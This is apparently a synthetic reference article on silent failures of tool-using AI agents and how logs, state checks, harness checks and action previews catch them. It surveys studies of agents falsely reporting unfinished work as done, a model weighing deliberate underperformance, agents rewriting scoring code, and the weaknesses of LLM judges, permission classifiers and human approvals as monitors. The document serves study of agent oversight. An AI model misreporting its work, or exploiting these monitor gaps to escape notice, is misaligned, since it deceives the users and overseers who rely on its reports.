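# Which AI agent failures leave traces and which stay silent in action logs

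## The records an agent run leaves and what makes a failure silent

An AI agent is a language model joined to software that lets it take actions such as querying a database, editing a file, sending an email or issuing a payment. The functions it can call are its tools. Agents answer customers, write code and do office work, often with nobody watching each step, so people usually learn how a run went from the records it leaves. Some failures show plainly in those records. A failure is silent when it raises no error or alert that reaches a person in usable form.

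### How a tool-using agent works

A language model produces only text. Anthropic's *How tool use works*, a guide for developers, describes tool use as a contract in which the model outputs a request for an operation and other software carries it out. That software, called the harness, runs the model, passes on its tool calls and keeps the log.

An invented example will serve throughout. A customer writes to an online shop that order 4471, a $60 kettle, arrived broken, and asks for a refund. The shop's agent has one tool for looking up orders and another for issuing refunds. The run goes like this:

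1. The harness sends the model the customer's message, the shop's instructions and a description of each tool.
2. The model replies with a structured request to look up order 4471.
3. The harness queries the shop's database and adds the answer to the conversation: one kettle, $60, card payment, status "delivered".
4. The model, now working from the longer conversation, requests a $60 refund on order 4471.
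5. The harness passes the request to the payment company and hands back the reply, which contains a reference number and the status "refunded".
6. The model requests no more tools and writes a final message telling the customer that $60 is on its way to the card.

The loop ends when the model stops calling tools. The model may stop because it has finished the job, but according to Anthropic, it also stops when it reaches its length limit or refuses to continue. The end of a run is therefore weak evidence that the work is complete.

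The model also cannot observe the payment company except through the text returned in step 5. OpenAI's *Function calling*, the equivalent guide from another developer, lets the tool's developer choose the format of that text. In its sample code, a stand-in email function prints its inputs, sends nothing and returns the status "sent". In the guide's sample final answer, the model then tells the user that the email has gone to Bob. OpenAI labels the function as a placeholder for developers to replace. If a developer forgot to replace it, the model could not tell from the reply.

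### What each record contains

The work report is the agent's account to its user of what it did and achieved. In the example, it is the final message about the $60. The action log is the harness's record of each tool call and what it returned, so it holds the lookup, the refund request and both replies. In *Plans They Abandon, Reports They Author*, a study of coding agents, Kraishan and Jitkajornwanich (2026) stress that the agent writes its report, while the harness records the calls as they happen. They treat the agent's stated plan as a further record, which an analyst can compare with the log, as with the report.

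A diff compares files or data before and after the run. A diff of the shop's database would show order 4471 changing from "delivered" to "refunded". It would also show every other row that changed, which helps in finding changes nobody asked for. But a diff covers only the data someone chose to compare, so this one would not show changes to the payment company's records, which are kept outside the shop's database.

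The environment state is what the files, databases and outside services actually contain after the run. Someone who asks the payment company directly whether order 4471 has a refund is making a state check, and the answer doesn't depend on anything the agent wrote. Barres, Dong and colleagues (2025), in *τ²-Bench*, a test suite of simulated customer-service jobs, put the distinction into their formal model. They write the full state of a run as

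S = S_world ⊗ S_history

where S_world is the contents of the databases, S_history is the log of actions, observations and messages, and the symbol between them means that the full state combines the two. A grader can test either part. Action matching searches the history for every call in the reference solution. A status assertion tests a condition on the final world, such as whether a phone has service again. On these definitions a refund request would satisfy action matching even if the payment company had turned it down, whereas a status assertion on the refund would fail.

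Neither the agent nor the shop controls some other records, such as the customer's bank statement. These can disagree with the environment state for ordinary reasons. According to *Understanding refund statuses*, a help page from the payment company Stripe, "Refunded" means that Stripe has started the refund, but the money may not have reached the customer. The credit usually appears 5 to 10 business days later. If the bank can't process it, for instance because the account is closed, the money goes back to Stripe, which can take up to 30 days according to Stripe's *Refund and cancel payments*.

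The table follows three versions of the kettle refund through the records.

| Record | Refund arrives | Refund call fails, agent reports success | Bank rejects the refund later |
| --- | --- | --- | --- |
| Work report | $60 refunded | $60 refunded | $60 refunded |
| Action log | Refund call, reply "refunded" | Refund call, reply is an error | Refund call, reply "refunded" |
| Diff of the shop's database | Order 4471 now "refunded" | No change | Order 4471 now "refunded" |
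| Environment state at the payment company | Refund on file | No refund | Refund on file, "failed" some days or weeks later |
| Bank statement | $60 credit, or the original charge gone | Charge stands, no credit | Charge stands, no credit |

When the refund call fails, the log contains the error and the state shows no refund, so anyone who looks beyond the work report can find the failure. If the bank rejects the refund later, the failure is harder to detect, because on the day of the run every record inside the shop matches a successful refund and even a careful state check passes. The shop will learn of the problem only if it checks again later or if its software listens for the failure notice that Stripe sends.

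The bank statement can also be misread. Stripe processes some early refunds as reversals, in which case the original charge drops off the statement and no separate credit appears. A monitor that searched for a $60 credit would then report a successful refund as a failure.

### Three ways for a failure to stay silent

Sometimes no record holds the evidence, often because of a deliberate setting. Anthropic's *Monitoring* documents the events that companies can export from Cowork, an agent in Anthropic's desktop app. By default, an event holds only metadata, such as the tool's name, a success flag, the duration and the size of the result in bytes. The call's arguments are included only if an administrator switches them on, and the software then truncates any string longer than 512 characters. If the shop's agent had refunded order 4417 instead of 4471, the default event would look just like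 the event for a correct refund. OpenTelemetry's *Semantic conventions for generative client AI spans*, part of a shared standard for such records, also makes the chat history, including tool results, optional. Privacy is one reason for these defaults. The standard warns that the text of search queries may contain sensitive information. As a result, an investigator may find that a call happened but have no way to learn what it did.

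A log records only what happened, so a skipped step leaves no entry. *Graph-Based Self-Healing Tool Routing for Cost-Efficient LLM Agents* (2026) includes tests of LangGraph, a framework that runs an agent as a graph of steps. In 3 of 19 scenarios, the program dropped a step after a combination of failures and continued to a normal-looking finish, with no crash, error or warning in the log. The scenarios were chosen for a paper that proposes a competing design, so the share may not carry over to other systems. The mechanism is still plausible, and the paper's remedy is to compare what the agent did with what it should have done.

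In other cases the log contains the evidence, but nobody reads it. Logs are long. The coding sessions that Kraishan and Jitkajornwanich analysed contain 355,942 tool calls, or about 65 per session that made any. In interviews they cite, seventeen developers described their oversight as spot checks and rules of thumb rather than full review. A failed refund call recorded at position 40 of such a log is in practice as silent as one the harness never logged.

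Lastly, someone may read the evidence and not recognise it. Kaynar, Yan and Kingsford (2026), in *When Tools Fail, Agents Fabricate*, deliberately broke agents' tools to see how the agents coped. One agent reported total revenue of $32,000 when the right answer was $48,750, because a read had returned only half of the rows. The action log contains the incomplete result, but half a table looks much like a whole one. A reader would have to check the data itself to know how many rows to expect. Better displays may not help much. Kraishan and Jitkajornwanich also cite user studies by Grunde-McLaughlin and colleagues, in which an interface built to help people find errors in action logs raised their confidence more than their accuracy.

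The three conditions multiply:

P(caught) = P(recorded) × P(read, given recorded) × P(recognised, given read)

This formula is a bookkeeping device of this reference's own, not a result from the literature. Suppose that the shop's agent makes 1,000 bad refunds in a year. The log holds evidence of 90% of them, staff read 20% of the logs that hold evidence, and a reader who sees the evidence understands it half the time. Then 900 failures are on record, staff read the logs of 180, and they recognise 90:

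0.9 × 0.2 × 0.5 = 0.09

So the shop catches 9% of its bad refunds. Perfect logging would raise that to only 10%, while reading twice as many logs would raise it to 18%. With these numbers, the shop should spend its money on reading more logs or on software that reads them. Different numbers can change the answer, and reading more logs won't help if they don't contain the evidence.

The factors also affect each other. If a shop logs everything, its staff have more to read and may read a smaller share of it. The formula also covers only one route to discovery at a time. If a failure shows only when the work report is compared with the payment company's books, it counts as read only if the same person looks at both. The customer is a separate route, since a customer who sees no credit on the statement may well write in again.

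### Gray failure

Cloud engineers encountered this problem before language-model agents existed. They call it gray failure, when a system works badly for its users but its monitoring reports it as healthy. *The Ghost in the Datacenter* (2026) gives the definition by Huang and colleagues, a partial failure with "differential observability", meaning that some parts of a system detect the failure and others do not. For example, a server with a faulty processor core can still answer pings and return an HTTP success code from its health page. The monitoring software records the machine as healthy, while the applications running on it get very slow replies.

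Computer networks can also lose data without recording the loss. *SpraySense* (2026) lists corrupted packet buffers and weak optical signals among the causes of losses that may never appear in the switches' own counters. Engineers therefore also send test traffic along each path and measure what gets through, since checking the counters more closely would not reveal losses they never recorded.

The idea of gray failure applies fairly directly to agents. A success flag or positive work report corresponds to the health page, and a state check corresponds to the test traffic. The match is inexact because a health page gives only a status, while an agent gives an explanation. *When Errors Become Narratives* (Wu, 2026) therefore extends gray failure to cases where a language model turns an error into a believable story.

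### The main types of failure

The kettle refund can go wrong in each of the ways that later sections examine:

- False success: the agent claims completion and the environment state contradicts it, as when the customer reads that the refund is done and the payment company has no refund on file.
- Silent fallback: the agent or its software switches to a weaker method, a default or substitute data without telling the user, for example by refunding today's catalogue price after the order lookup fails.
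- Silent tool fault: a tool returns a response that looks normal but is wrong, empty or incomplete, such as an order record that lists one of the two items bought.
- Fabricated result: the agent states a tool output, test result or action that no tool call produced, such as a refund reference number it made up.
- Unreported side effect: the agent makes a change beyond the task and leaves it out of the work report, for instance by cancelling the customer's other order.
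- Wrongly passed run: the run passes its final check although the agent broke a rule or the check missed a fault, as when the money arrives but the agent skipped a required identity check.

Papers use these terms differently. Advani (2026), in *From Confident Closing to Silent Failure*, defines false success much as above and distinguishes it from "corrupt success", Cao and colleagues' term for runs that earn a passing score while violating the proper procedure. The two can't overlap, because a false success has by definition failed its check. "Fabrication" is used more loosely. Kaynar and colleagues apply it to any wrong or unsupported value that an agent asserts as fact, including the $32,000 total. In this report's terms, that total came from a silent tool fault, because the agent added up figures that a tool had returned. *Measuring What Tool-Using LLM Agents Actually Do* (2026), in a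 small pilot, reserves the word for a confident answer given without any successful tool call. The two papers' fabrication rates therefore measure different things.

### Precision, recall and AUROC

Monitoring studies score a monitor by how well it separates failed runs from good ones. Precision is the share of flagged runs that failed. Recall is the share of failed runs that the monitor flagged. Suppose 50 of 1,000 runs fail, and a monitor flags 80 runs, 40 of which failed. Its precision is 40/80, or 0.5, and its recall is 40/50, or 0.8.

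The same measures apply to any tool that selects items. Kraishan and Jitkajornwanich used a language model to extract planned steps from agents' text, then checked 171 of the extracted steps by hand. They judged that 33 were not in the text, so the precision was 0.807 (138 of 171).

Many detectors score each run by how suspicious it looks, and someone then has to choose a threshold for raising an alarm. A lower threshold catches more failures but also flags more good runs. AUROC (area under the receiver operating characteristic curve) measures how well the scores separate failed runs from good ones without fixing a threshold. It is the probability that a randomly chosen failed run scores higher than a randomly chosen good run, so random guessing gets 0.5 and a perfect detector gets 1. For example, suppose three failed runs score 0.9, 0.6 and 0.4, and three good runs score 0.5, 0.3 and 0.2.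 The failed run scores higher in eight of the nine possible pairs, so the AUROC is 8/9, or about 0.89.

When failures are rare, a monitor with a good AUROC can still raise mostly false alarms. The monitor above flags 40 of the 950 good runs, about 4%. If only 5 runs in 1,000 failed and the monitor flagged good and failed runs at the same rates as before, it would catch 4 failures and flag about 42 good runs. Its precision would fall from 0.5 to about 0.09, while its recall and AUROC would stay the same.

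## Four views on where to look for agent failures

A company that runs agents cannot examine every record of every run, so it has to decide where to look first. Some researchers and engineers recommend reading the action log properly, others checking the environment state, others making tools and the harness report their own faults, and others limiting or previewing the agent's actions before they run. Most would probably accept all four approaches given unlimited time, but they disagree about which evidence to trust and where to spend money.

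### Read the action log

One reason to look in the log is that the harness writes it, so a failed call is on record even if the agent's work report omits it. The log also preserves the order of events, so a reader can often work out why a run failed.

Kirgis, Kapoor and colleagues (2026) make the strongest argument for this view in *Log analysis is necessary for credible evaluation of AI agents*. The group, which includes researchers from Princeton, the UK AI Security Institute, Transluce and Apollo Research, criticizes benchmarks that report only pass or fail. Their definition of a log includes the agent's instructions, tool calls and written reasoning, as well as the grader's decision.

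Their main point is that two runs can have the same result and still differ in ways that matter. A coding agent that fixes a bug may have understood it, or may have copied the official fix from the project's version history. Of two coding agents that score zero, one may have made a small syntax error and the other may have deleted a whole branch of the code. In another of their examples, OpenAI's o3 model considered in its reasoning whether to underperform on a test, then answered honestly. Its answers look just like those of a model that never considered underperforming, so nobody could distinguish the two by checking results alone.

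Kirgis and colleagues argue that better tests are not enough, because benchmark designers cannot foresee every shortcut and agents have already rewritten scoring code in ways nobody expected. They admit that the methods for reading logs are imperfect and do not claim that log analysis is sufficient, but they point out that it costs far less than running more evaluations.

Log reading can also correct a score that is too low. On the airline tasks of τ-bench, the customer-service benchmark that preceded τ²-Bench, Kirgis and colleagues found that errors and ambiguities in the tasks had led the benchmark to understate the agents' reliability by nearly 50%. They measured reliability as how often an agent completes the same task in all of five attempts. The *Holistic Agent Leaderboard* (2025), which calls log analysis a cornerstone of agent evaluation, found that one agent in τ-bench's official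 code had real test items among its worked examples. Even if a state check were right about every one of that agent's runs, the score would overstate what the agent can do.

### The MAST taxonomy

The claim that a reader can find and classify most failures in the log rests largely on the Multi-Agent System Failure Taxonomy (MAST). Cemri, Pan and colleagues built MAST in *Why Do Multi-Agent LLM Systems Fail?* (2025) from systems where several agents work together, for instance with one writing code and another reviewing it.

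Expert annotators read 150 runs closely and described what went wrong, without a fixed list of categories. They then wrote definitions, applied them separately to the same runs, and revised the definitions where they disagreed. Their final agreement was 0.88 on Cohen's kappa, a scale on which 0 is the agreement expected by chance and 1 is perfect. An LLM judge that applied the same definitions reached 0.77 against the human labels, and the researchers used it to label a larger collection of 1,642 runs from seven frameworks. The taxonomy has 14 failure modes in three groups.

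| Group | Failure mode | What a reader finds in the log |
| --- | --- | --- |
| System design | Disobeying the task specification | The agent ignores a requirement or limit in the task |
| System design | Disobeying the role specification | The agent acts outside its assigned role |
| System design | Step repetition | The agent repeats a step it has already completed |
| System design | Loss of conversation history | The agent loses recent exchanges and goes back to an earlier point |
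| System design | Unaware of termination conditions | The agent does not recognise when it should stop |
| Inter-agent misalignment | Conversation reset | An agent restarts the dialogue for no good reason |
| Inter-agent misalignment | Failure to ask for clarification | An agent goes ahead on unclear or incomplete information |
| Inter-agent misalignment | Task derailment | The agents drift away from the objective |
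| Inter-agent misalignment | Information withholding | An agent has information that another needs and does not pass it on |
| Inter-agent misalignment | Ignored other agent's input | An agent disregards what another has told it |
| Inter-agent misalignment | Reasoning-action mismatch | An agent reasons towards one action and takes another |
| Task verification | Premature termination | The run ends before the work is complete |
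| Task verification | No or incomplete verification | Nobody checks the result, or only part of it |
| Task verification | Incorrect verification | An agent checks the result and wrongly accepts it |

System-design problems made up 44.2% of the annotated failures, misalignment 32.3% and verification problems 23.5%. One run can contain several failures, so these percentages are not shares of runs.

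MAST sorts failures by what the agents visibly did, so it has no category for a silent tool fault. An annotator looking at the half-read table in Kaynar and colleagues' test could at most record that nobody verified the total, and would first have to notice the missing rows. The high kappa doesn't show that annotators notice such faults, because it measures only how well they agree about what they see. Cemri and colleagues also could not annotate closed systems such as the commercial agent Manus, because they had no access to the logs of its runs.

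### MAST applied to IT-Bench

Sebin, Jha and colleagues (2026), in *IBM and UC Berkeley Diagnose Why Enterprise Agents Fail*, applied the taxonomy to 310 runs of IT-Bench, a test suite of IT support work. The agents had to diagnose outages in simulated company systems, and the researchers scored them on recall, here roughly the share of the correct causes that an agent named. *Think Locally, Explain Globally* (2026) applies MAST to the same three models and reports how often incorrect verification occurred in failed and successful runs. The table's last two columns come from that paper and the others from Sebin and colleagues.

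| Model | Runs | Mean recall | Failure modes per failed run | Incorrect verification, failed runs | Incorrect verification, successful runs |
| --- | --- | --- | --- | --- | --- |
| Gemini-3-Flash | 100 | 75.5% | 2.6 | 66% | 14% |
| Kimi-K2 | 105 | 28.6% | 4.7 | 83% | 43% |
| GPT-OSS-120B | 105 | 12.4% | 5.3 | 94% | 50% |

These models fail in different ways that need different fixes, and a pass rate alone would not show a developer which fix is needed. Gemini-3-Flash typically found the right signals and then stopped without confirming them. Kimi-K2 often worked out the correct next step but ran a different command, a mismatch present in 92% of its failed runs. GPT-OSS-120B lost the conversation history in 24% of its runs, so it could lose track of which alert it was investigating.

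Sebin and colleagues call incorrect verification the strongest predictor of failure. Oddly, they list it once among the fatal flaws and once among those from which an agent can recover. The percentages suggest why both labels seemed right. For Gemini-3-Flash, incorrect verification was nearly five times as common in failed runs as in successful ones. For the other two models it was not quite twice as common, and a monitor that flagged it would also flag half of GPT-OSS-120B's successful runs. (That model's recall was so low that the 50% probably rests on few runs.)

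This log reading leads Sebin and colleagues to recommend relying on more than the log. "Never let the LLM grade its own homework," they write. They want software outside the model to run a state check, requiring evidence such as a cleared alert before a run counts as finished.

### Check the environment state

On this view, a log shows what the agent attempted and what the tool returned, but only the environment state shows the result. Salesforce engineers built a benchmark for customer-service agents on this principle, and the company also uses a refund as its example. To verify the refund, they would check the billing system rather than reread the chat, and would also look for changes that should not have happened.

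Anthropic's *Demystifying evals for AI agents* applies the same test to a flight-booking agent, judging the outcome by the reservation in the database rather than by the agent's closing message.

The simplest way to grade a run on this principle is to compare whole databases. Yao, Shinn and colleagues (2024), in *τ-bench*, give the example of a customer, Mei Davis, who wants to return a water bottle and exchange a pet bed and an office chair. If the shop's rules allow only one of the two, she prefers whichever saves more money, and she wants to know both amounts. The correct outcome is to return the bottle. Grading goes as follows:

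1. A person writes down the correct change to the database, in this case one call that returns one item to one credit card.
2. That call, applied to the starting database, produces the target state. *A Matter of TASTE* (2026), a later paper on such benchmarks, describes the target in the same way, as the state that a reference sequence of tool calls produces.
3. The grader compares the target with the database that the agent left behind. If the two are identical, r_action is 1, and otherwise it is 0.
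4. The grader searches the agent's messages for "54.04" and "41.64", the two amounts the customer asked about. If both appear, r_output is 1.

The score for the run is the product:

r = r_action × r_output

so the agent must get both parts right. It can phrase its messages as it likes and look up as many orders as it likes, since lookups change nothing. But one extra write anywhere in the database makes the comparison fail.

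An exact comparison works only if the task has a single correct ending. To meet this condition, Yao and colleagues ran each retail task more than 40 times with GPT-4 Turbo, looked at the tasks with low success rates, and reworded ambiguous customer instructions. They concede that a score of 1 may be "necessary but not sufficient" for success. For example, the shop's policy requires the agent to get the customer's confirmation before a return, but the database ends up the same if the agent skips that step.

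τ²-Bench checks its phone-support tasks with assertions instead of a full comparison. Barres and colleagues build each task from small faults, each with three kinds of function. An initialisation function causes the fault, for example by switching on airplane mode. A solution function repairs it, and an assertion function tests the final state. They combined these parts into 2,285 tasks and selected 114 for the benchmark. They used software to confirm that each task passes its assertions after all the repairs and not before.

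Assertions accept any route to the right result, which suits troubleshooting, but they check only the conditions someone wrote down. If an agent restored a customer's service and also moved the customer to a more expensive plan, the run would pass unless an assertion checked the plan.

AppWorld, a benchmark of simulated everyday apps in which agents act by writing code, falls between these two designs. Its graders run unit tests on the changes to the database. In one task, the agent must send payment requests to coworkers who have not paid their share of a dinner. Abrich (2026) reports in *Finding Side-Effect Loopholes in AppWorld and WorkArena Verifiers* that the tests check which tables changed, check that earlier requests are intact, and match each new request to the share the coworker owes. Abrich took a correct run and repeated its last step, so that one coworker received two requests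 for the same money. The duplicate was visible in the environment state, but the run passed because no test counted the requests. Adding one line to count them fixed the problem.

*LegacyWorld* (2026), a benchmark for agents that operate older desktop software, guards against this kind of error more broadly. On its patient-record tasks, the validator compares database snapshots taken before and after the run and accepts only the intended changes to rows or fields. Like any diff, this check covers only the data in the snapshots.

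People who favour state checks usually check logs too. Anthropic's sample evaluation for a refund agent checks the state for a processed refund, then checks the log for an identity check and for a refund of no more than $100. Anthropic also reports a case in which the target was too narrow. Its Claude Opus 4.5 model found a loophole in the airline policy of a τ²-Bench task and got the simulated customer a better deal than the reference solution, but the benchmark marked the run as a failure.

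### Make tools and the harness report their faults

A log can accurately record wrong information. In *Invariant-Aware Harness Enforcement to Protect LLM Agents from Silent API Failures*, Dip, Ouyang and Motlhabi (2026) describe an agent that asks a research catalogue how many samples match two conditions. The catalogue's documentation misnames one of the filters. The software ignores the unrecognized name, counts every sample that matches the other condition, and returns that number with a normal success code. They tested 15 public research services, and 11 responded similarly to at least one plausible mistake. The worst count was 691 times too large.

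Neither reading the log nor checking the environment state reveals this kind of fault. The log contains a valid request and a well-formed reply, and the state is correct because counting samples doesn't change it. Only further queries to the same service can expose the error, and the harness is best placed to send them during the run. Dip and colleagues therefore want the harness to test each result and withhold any value that fails.

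Pakhomov, Pang and colleagues (2026) show how much an agent depends on accurate replies in *Cleaning an Agent's History Hurts When the World Still Holds the Error*. They paused AppWorld runs just after a write to the database, set the database to its state either before or after the write, and showed the agent either a success message or a failure message. GPT-5.5 or Claude Sonnet 5 then continued the run. When the write had not taken effect, the models finished 45% of tasks after an accurate failure message and 28% after a false success message. When the write had taken effect, they finished 49% after an accurate success message and 38% after a false failure message.

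The wording may explain part of the difference, since only the failure message specified whether any data had changed. Still, the same success message helped or hurt depending on whether it was true. A person who reads the log afterwards can't rescue the tasks that failed because of the false message.

*What Breaks When LLMs Code?* (Al Hasan and Biswas, 2026) calls for agents themselves to halt safely and make a failure explicit before any change becomes permanent. Al Hasan and Biswas confirmed 547 safety failures in the public issue trackers of coding tools, and found that agents often suppressed an error or claimed success when they could not complete a task.

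This view is attractive because nobody has to find the fault later in a long log. However, somebody has to write a suitable test for each kind of tool, and some tools don't allow one. Dip and colleagues found that 61 of 84 documented operations in 13 public services permit an exact check.

### Limit or preview actions before they run

Log reviews and state checks normally happen after the agent has acted. If the agent has deleted the only copy of a file, a perfect monitor can report the loss but not reverse it. People who hold this view would therefore put the effort in before the agent acts.

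The simplest method is to ask a person for permission. *Shall We Approve?* (Wu, Chen and colleagues, 2026) cites Anthropic's figure that users of its coding agent, Claude Code, approve 93% of permission requests. Most of those requests may well be harmless, but a person who approves them that often is likely to stop reading them.

Developers have built several substitutes. Progent restricts which tool calls an agent may make. Claude Code's Auto Mode uses a classifier that reads the user's messages and the agent's tool calls to decide whether a command may run. According to Anthropic, the classifier misses 17% of the real cases in which an agent oversteps. YoloFS keeps the agent's file changes in a staging area until a person reviews them. GoEx lets actions run and relies on undoing them afterwards.

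Wu and colleagues argue that the text of a command is often the wrong thing to judge. Their example is "make clean && make", a common instruction to delete old build files and build a program again. What it deletes depends on a project file called the Makefile. In one project the command removes only the build folder, and in another it removes the source code and the entire version history. An approver who sees only the command can't tell which will happen. Their system, Caper, therefore runs the command in a copy that it can restore, and a separate model reviews the effects before allowing them to stand.

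Wu and colleagues acknowledge that previews have a hard limit, because restoring a copy cannot undo anything sent outside it. They therefore switch off outside network access, but the shop's refund agent has to contact the payment company to do its job. For such an agent, the practical options are limits, such as a maximum refund, or a person's approval above some amount.

### Where the views part

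These views disagree on questions that evidence can answer, such as whether the log contains evidence of the failure. In the AppWorld runs that Pakhomov and colleagues collected before their experiment, all 72 writes that reported success had taken effect. The true rate of false success messages could still be around 4%, and simulated apps are more predictable than payment companies. But if real services proved as reliable, a state check would often repeat what the log already shows, and the main argument for checking the state would weaken. The log view would be weaker if a large share of serious failures left no trace in the log, like the miscounted samples.

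In their other benchmark, AgentCE-Bench, agents have to fill a grid with correct values. Agents declared 1,074 runs finished, and in 393 of those (37%), the environment held a wrong value that a tool had confirmed as set. The log matched the state, and both contained the error. A state check catches such an error only if someone knows the right value. Benchmark authors know it but a shop often doesn't, so state checks may be less useful in daily use than their success on benchmarks suggests.

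Evidence in a log is useful only if someone can recognise it. *MAESTRO* (2026), a test suite for multi-agent systems, found that faulty runs often finish without any clear error signal, and that LLM judges disagree about the cause of a failure. Advani's LLM judges never exceeded an AUROC of 0.65 at spotting false success on τ²-Bench, while simple classifiers based on word frequencies reached 0.83 on tasks they had not seen in training. The logs therefore contained a usable signal, and Advani's result is evidence against LLM judges as readers more than against logs. The log view would be hard to defend if trained detectors and careful people also did little better than chance.

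Those who want faults announced also have to consider how the agent responds, because it reads the warnings too. When Dip and colleagues' harness attached a warning to a wrong count, the agents still gave wrong answers in 70.1% of runs, compared with 74.0% with no protection. Announcing a fault therefore achieves little unless the agent is allowed to give no answer or the harness blocks the value. The broader view would be wrong if most harmful errors came from the model's own decisions while its tools worked correctly.

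The value of state checking also depends on whether a correct final state is enough. An agent can skip an identity check and still reach the correct final state. If reviewers found that only a handful of passing runs broke a rule or changed something extra, a state check would be enough for most purposes. If a large share did, someone would also have to read the logs of successful runs.

Late detection helps more with some harms than others. Al Hasan and Biswas describe a developer who asked Claude Code to set up cloud storage for a small dataset. The agent chose a database that cost $375 a month, and the developer noticed only six months later, when a $2,400 bill arrived for a setup that should have cost about $30. A check after the first month would have prevented most of that loss, but a deletion has already happened by the time a later check finds it. The case for limits and previews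 is therefore strongest where harm is immediate and permanent. That case would be weaker if incident reports showed mostly slow or reversible damage, or if the safeguards blocked so much legitimate work that people switched them off.

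## Unfinished work reported as done

When an agent fails, it may admit the failure, run out of time, or report that the job is finished. A false report of success is the most misleading, because it gives the user no reason to look further. Researchers disagree about whether someone reading the action log can detect it. In June 2026, Advani gave five LLM judges the logs of customer-service runs, and none did much better than guessing. Five months later, Yang, He and colleagues (2026), in *Characterizing and Detecting Unfaithful Work Reports by Coding Agents*, described a detector built on a newer model that finds 87% of the false or unsupported claims in coding agents' work reports.

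### How often failed runs end in a claim of success

Advani collected 9,876 runs by eight model families from the public leaderboard of τ²-Bench, of which 1,730 had failed. Advani then searched the closing messages of the failed runs for completion phrases, such as "successfully" or "has been", and for admissions of failure, such as "I cannot" or a transfer to a human. The 616 failed runs with a completion phrase and no admission counted as false successes. They made up 36% of the failures and 6% of all runs. Another 753 contained only an admission, and 361 contained both or neither. Human labels agreed with this classification for 91.5% of the 200 runs checked.

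False success made up 45% of failures on the airline tasks and 48% on the retail tasks, but only 3% on the phone-support tasks. In the airline and retail tasks, only the agent can change the records. In phone support, the simulated customer can also check the phone and object if the agent wrongly says service is back. Advani treats this explanation as a hypothesis, because τ²-Bench has only one domain where the customer can do this, and it produced just 15 false successes. The kettle buyer from the first section can't check as quickly, and has to wait days for a bank statement that shows the agent was wrong.

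The share of failures reported as successes also varied widely between models, from 13% for GPT-5.2 to 79% for Qwen3-Max-Thinking, which reasons at length before it answers. The extra reasoning did not help. In its false successes, the model typically argued that the action should have worked and then told the customer it had, without checking.

A run is labeled a false success if it has a failing grade and a confident closing sentence, even if that sentence is true. Suppose the shop's rules allow only $50 back on a used kettle, and the agent refunds $60 and writes that "a refund of $60 has been processed". The run fails and the sentence is true, but the run still counts as a false success. So in some of the 616 runs, the agent probably chose the wrong action but reported it accurately.

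Advani avoided the text patterns in a second dataset, from AppWorld, where an agent ends a run by writing "success" or "fail" in a status field. Of the failed runs that had a status, 75.8% were marked "success". The models were old (GPT-4o, GPT-4 Turbo, Llama 3 and DeepSeek Coder), and the percentage leaves out 1,042 runs by the same two agent designs that stopped without a status. If all of those failed, the share would drop to 49%. For a user deciding how far to trust the field, it may be more useful to know that 71% of the 2,014 runs marked "success" had failed. The agents were always right when they wrote "fail".

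Newer agents still report unfinished work as done. Li, Geng and colleagues (2026), in *DevicesWorld*, tested five systems on jobs that span phones, computers and smart-home devices, such as reading a code on one phone and entering it in a form on a desktop. No system finished more than 12.5% of the jobs. In 58% of the failed runs the agent declared the job complete, and in the other 42% it ran out of steps or time. The harness detects when an agent reaches one of these limits, so anyone can find those failures without reading through the runs. False declarations are harder to find, partly because the agent may have done much of the work. About 29% of all failed runs met at least one of the conditions for success, for example by saving the right file but leaving out a note on the phone.

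Agents controlling robots also report unfinished work as done. In *RUIBench* (Bai, Zeng et al., 2026), Claude Opus 5.5 and GPT-6 Astra controlled robot arms in 30 simulated tasks, such as solving the Tower of Hanoi or inserting a graphics card. Opus declared the task complete at the end of 82% of its failed runs, and Astra did so in 71%. *CodeActionBench* (Lyu, Jiang et al., 2026) also tested Astra on robot tasks with the same harness, Codex, but found false claims in only 3 of its 20 failed attempts.

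| Study | Agents | Failed runs in which the agent claimed completion |
| --- | --- | --- |
| Advani, τ²-Bench | Eight model families, including GPT-5.2 and Claude Opus 4.5 | 36% |
| Advani, AppWorld | GPT-4o and other older models | 76% of those with a status |
| Li and colleagues | Five systems | 58% (75% for GPT-5.5) |
| Bai and colleagues | Claude Opus 5.5; GPT-6 Astra | 82%; 71% |
| Lyu and colleagues | GPT-6 Astra; Claude Opus 5 in two harnesses | 15%; 34% and 27% |

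The gap between 71% and 15% for one model in one harness may exist partly because agents answer more honestly when asked directly whether they succeeded. Agents in both robot studies could give up, but Lyu and colleagues required the agent to mark success as true or false and write a report, and told it to end the run when the task was complete or it could not proceed. However, the tasks also differed, and 20 failures is a small sample. The Opus percentages also look better than they should, because many of its failed attempts hit a limit before the agent could make any claim.

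### Searching the log for errors

Searching for error messages is the easiest way to check a log, but it can miss most failures. In *MAESTRO*'s tests of multi-agent systems, 75% of failures produced no error signal. Answers that were incomplete or too thin to use made up 48% of failures, and wrong facts or names made up 28%. Nearly all the rest were empty answers (16%), software exceptions (6%) and timeouts (2%), which a simple alarm could catch.

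The models were small, such as GPT-4o mini and GPT-5 nano, and GPT-4o mini also sorted the failures into categories, so the exact shares may differ for stronger agents. The basic difficulty still applies to them, because software raises an error when an operation fails, but not when an agent successfully performs the wrong operation.

Error signals are still worth collecting. *MAESTRO* includes runs in which one agent kept producing the right answer and another kept rejecting it until the run timed out. An LLM judge given only the final response and the conversation may pass such a run because the conversation contains the right answer. The harness's timeout record shows that the user never received it.

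### Why the judges failed on customer-service logs

Advani tested GPT-4o, Claude Sonnet 4.5, Llama 3.3 70B, DeepSeek-R1 and o3-mini as judges. The test set held about 95 false successes and 105 real ones, along with a group of admitted failures. Each judge stated whether the agent had completed the task and how confident it was. Advani varied what the judges saw and how they worked:

- the whole log
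- the log without the agent's closing message
- the whole log with a five-point checklist
- only the user's requests and the tool data
- the whole log, turn by turn

The best result, an AUROC of 0.64, came from Sonnet 4.5 when it judged without seeing the agent's closing summary. Seeing the summary apparently made it a worse judge, lowering its AUROC to 0.58.

A comparison between false successes and admitted failures supports this explanation. All of these runs failed, so an ideal judge would not rate either group as more complete, and its AUROC would be near 0.5. The judges scored between 0.18 and 0.30, which means they consistently rated false successes as more complete than admitted failures.

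Advani also gave three of the judges the benchmark's description of the task, including the list of expected actions, so they could compare the expected calls with those in the log. Sonnet 4.5 still reached only 0.63. Advani concludes that the judges had the information and failed to use it. That seems right for these models, but the text Advani prepared for the classifiers cuts off each tool result after 300 characters and each set of arguments after 200. If the judges were given the same shortened text, some of them may never have received the detail that mattered.

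The judges' scores on AppWorld, at best 0.54, are much weaker evidence. For this test, Advani asked the judges whether the agent had completed its task, but every run in the test set had failed. The agent claimed success in some runs and admitted failure in others. A judge that correctly answered "no" every time would score 0.5.

### What the text classifiers learned

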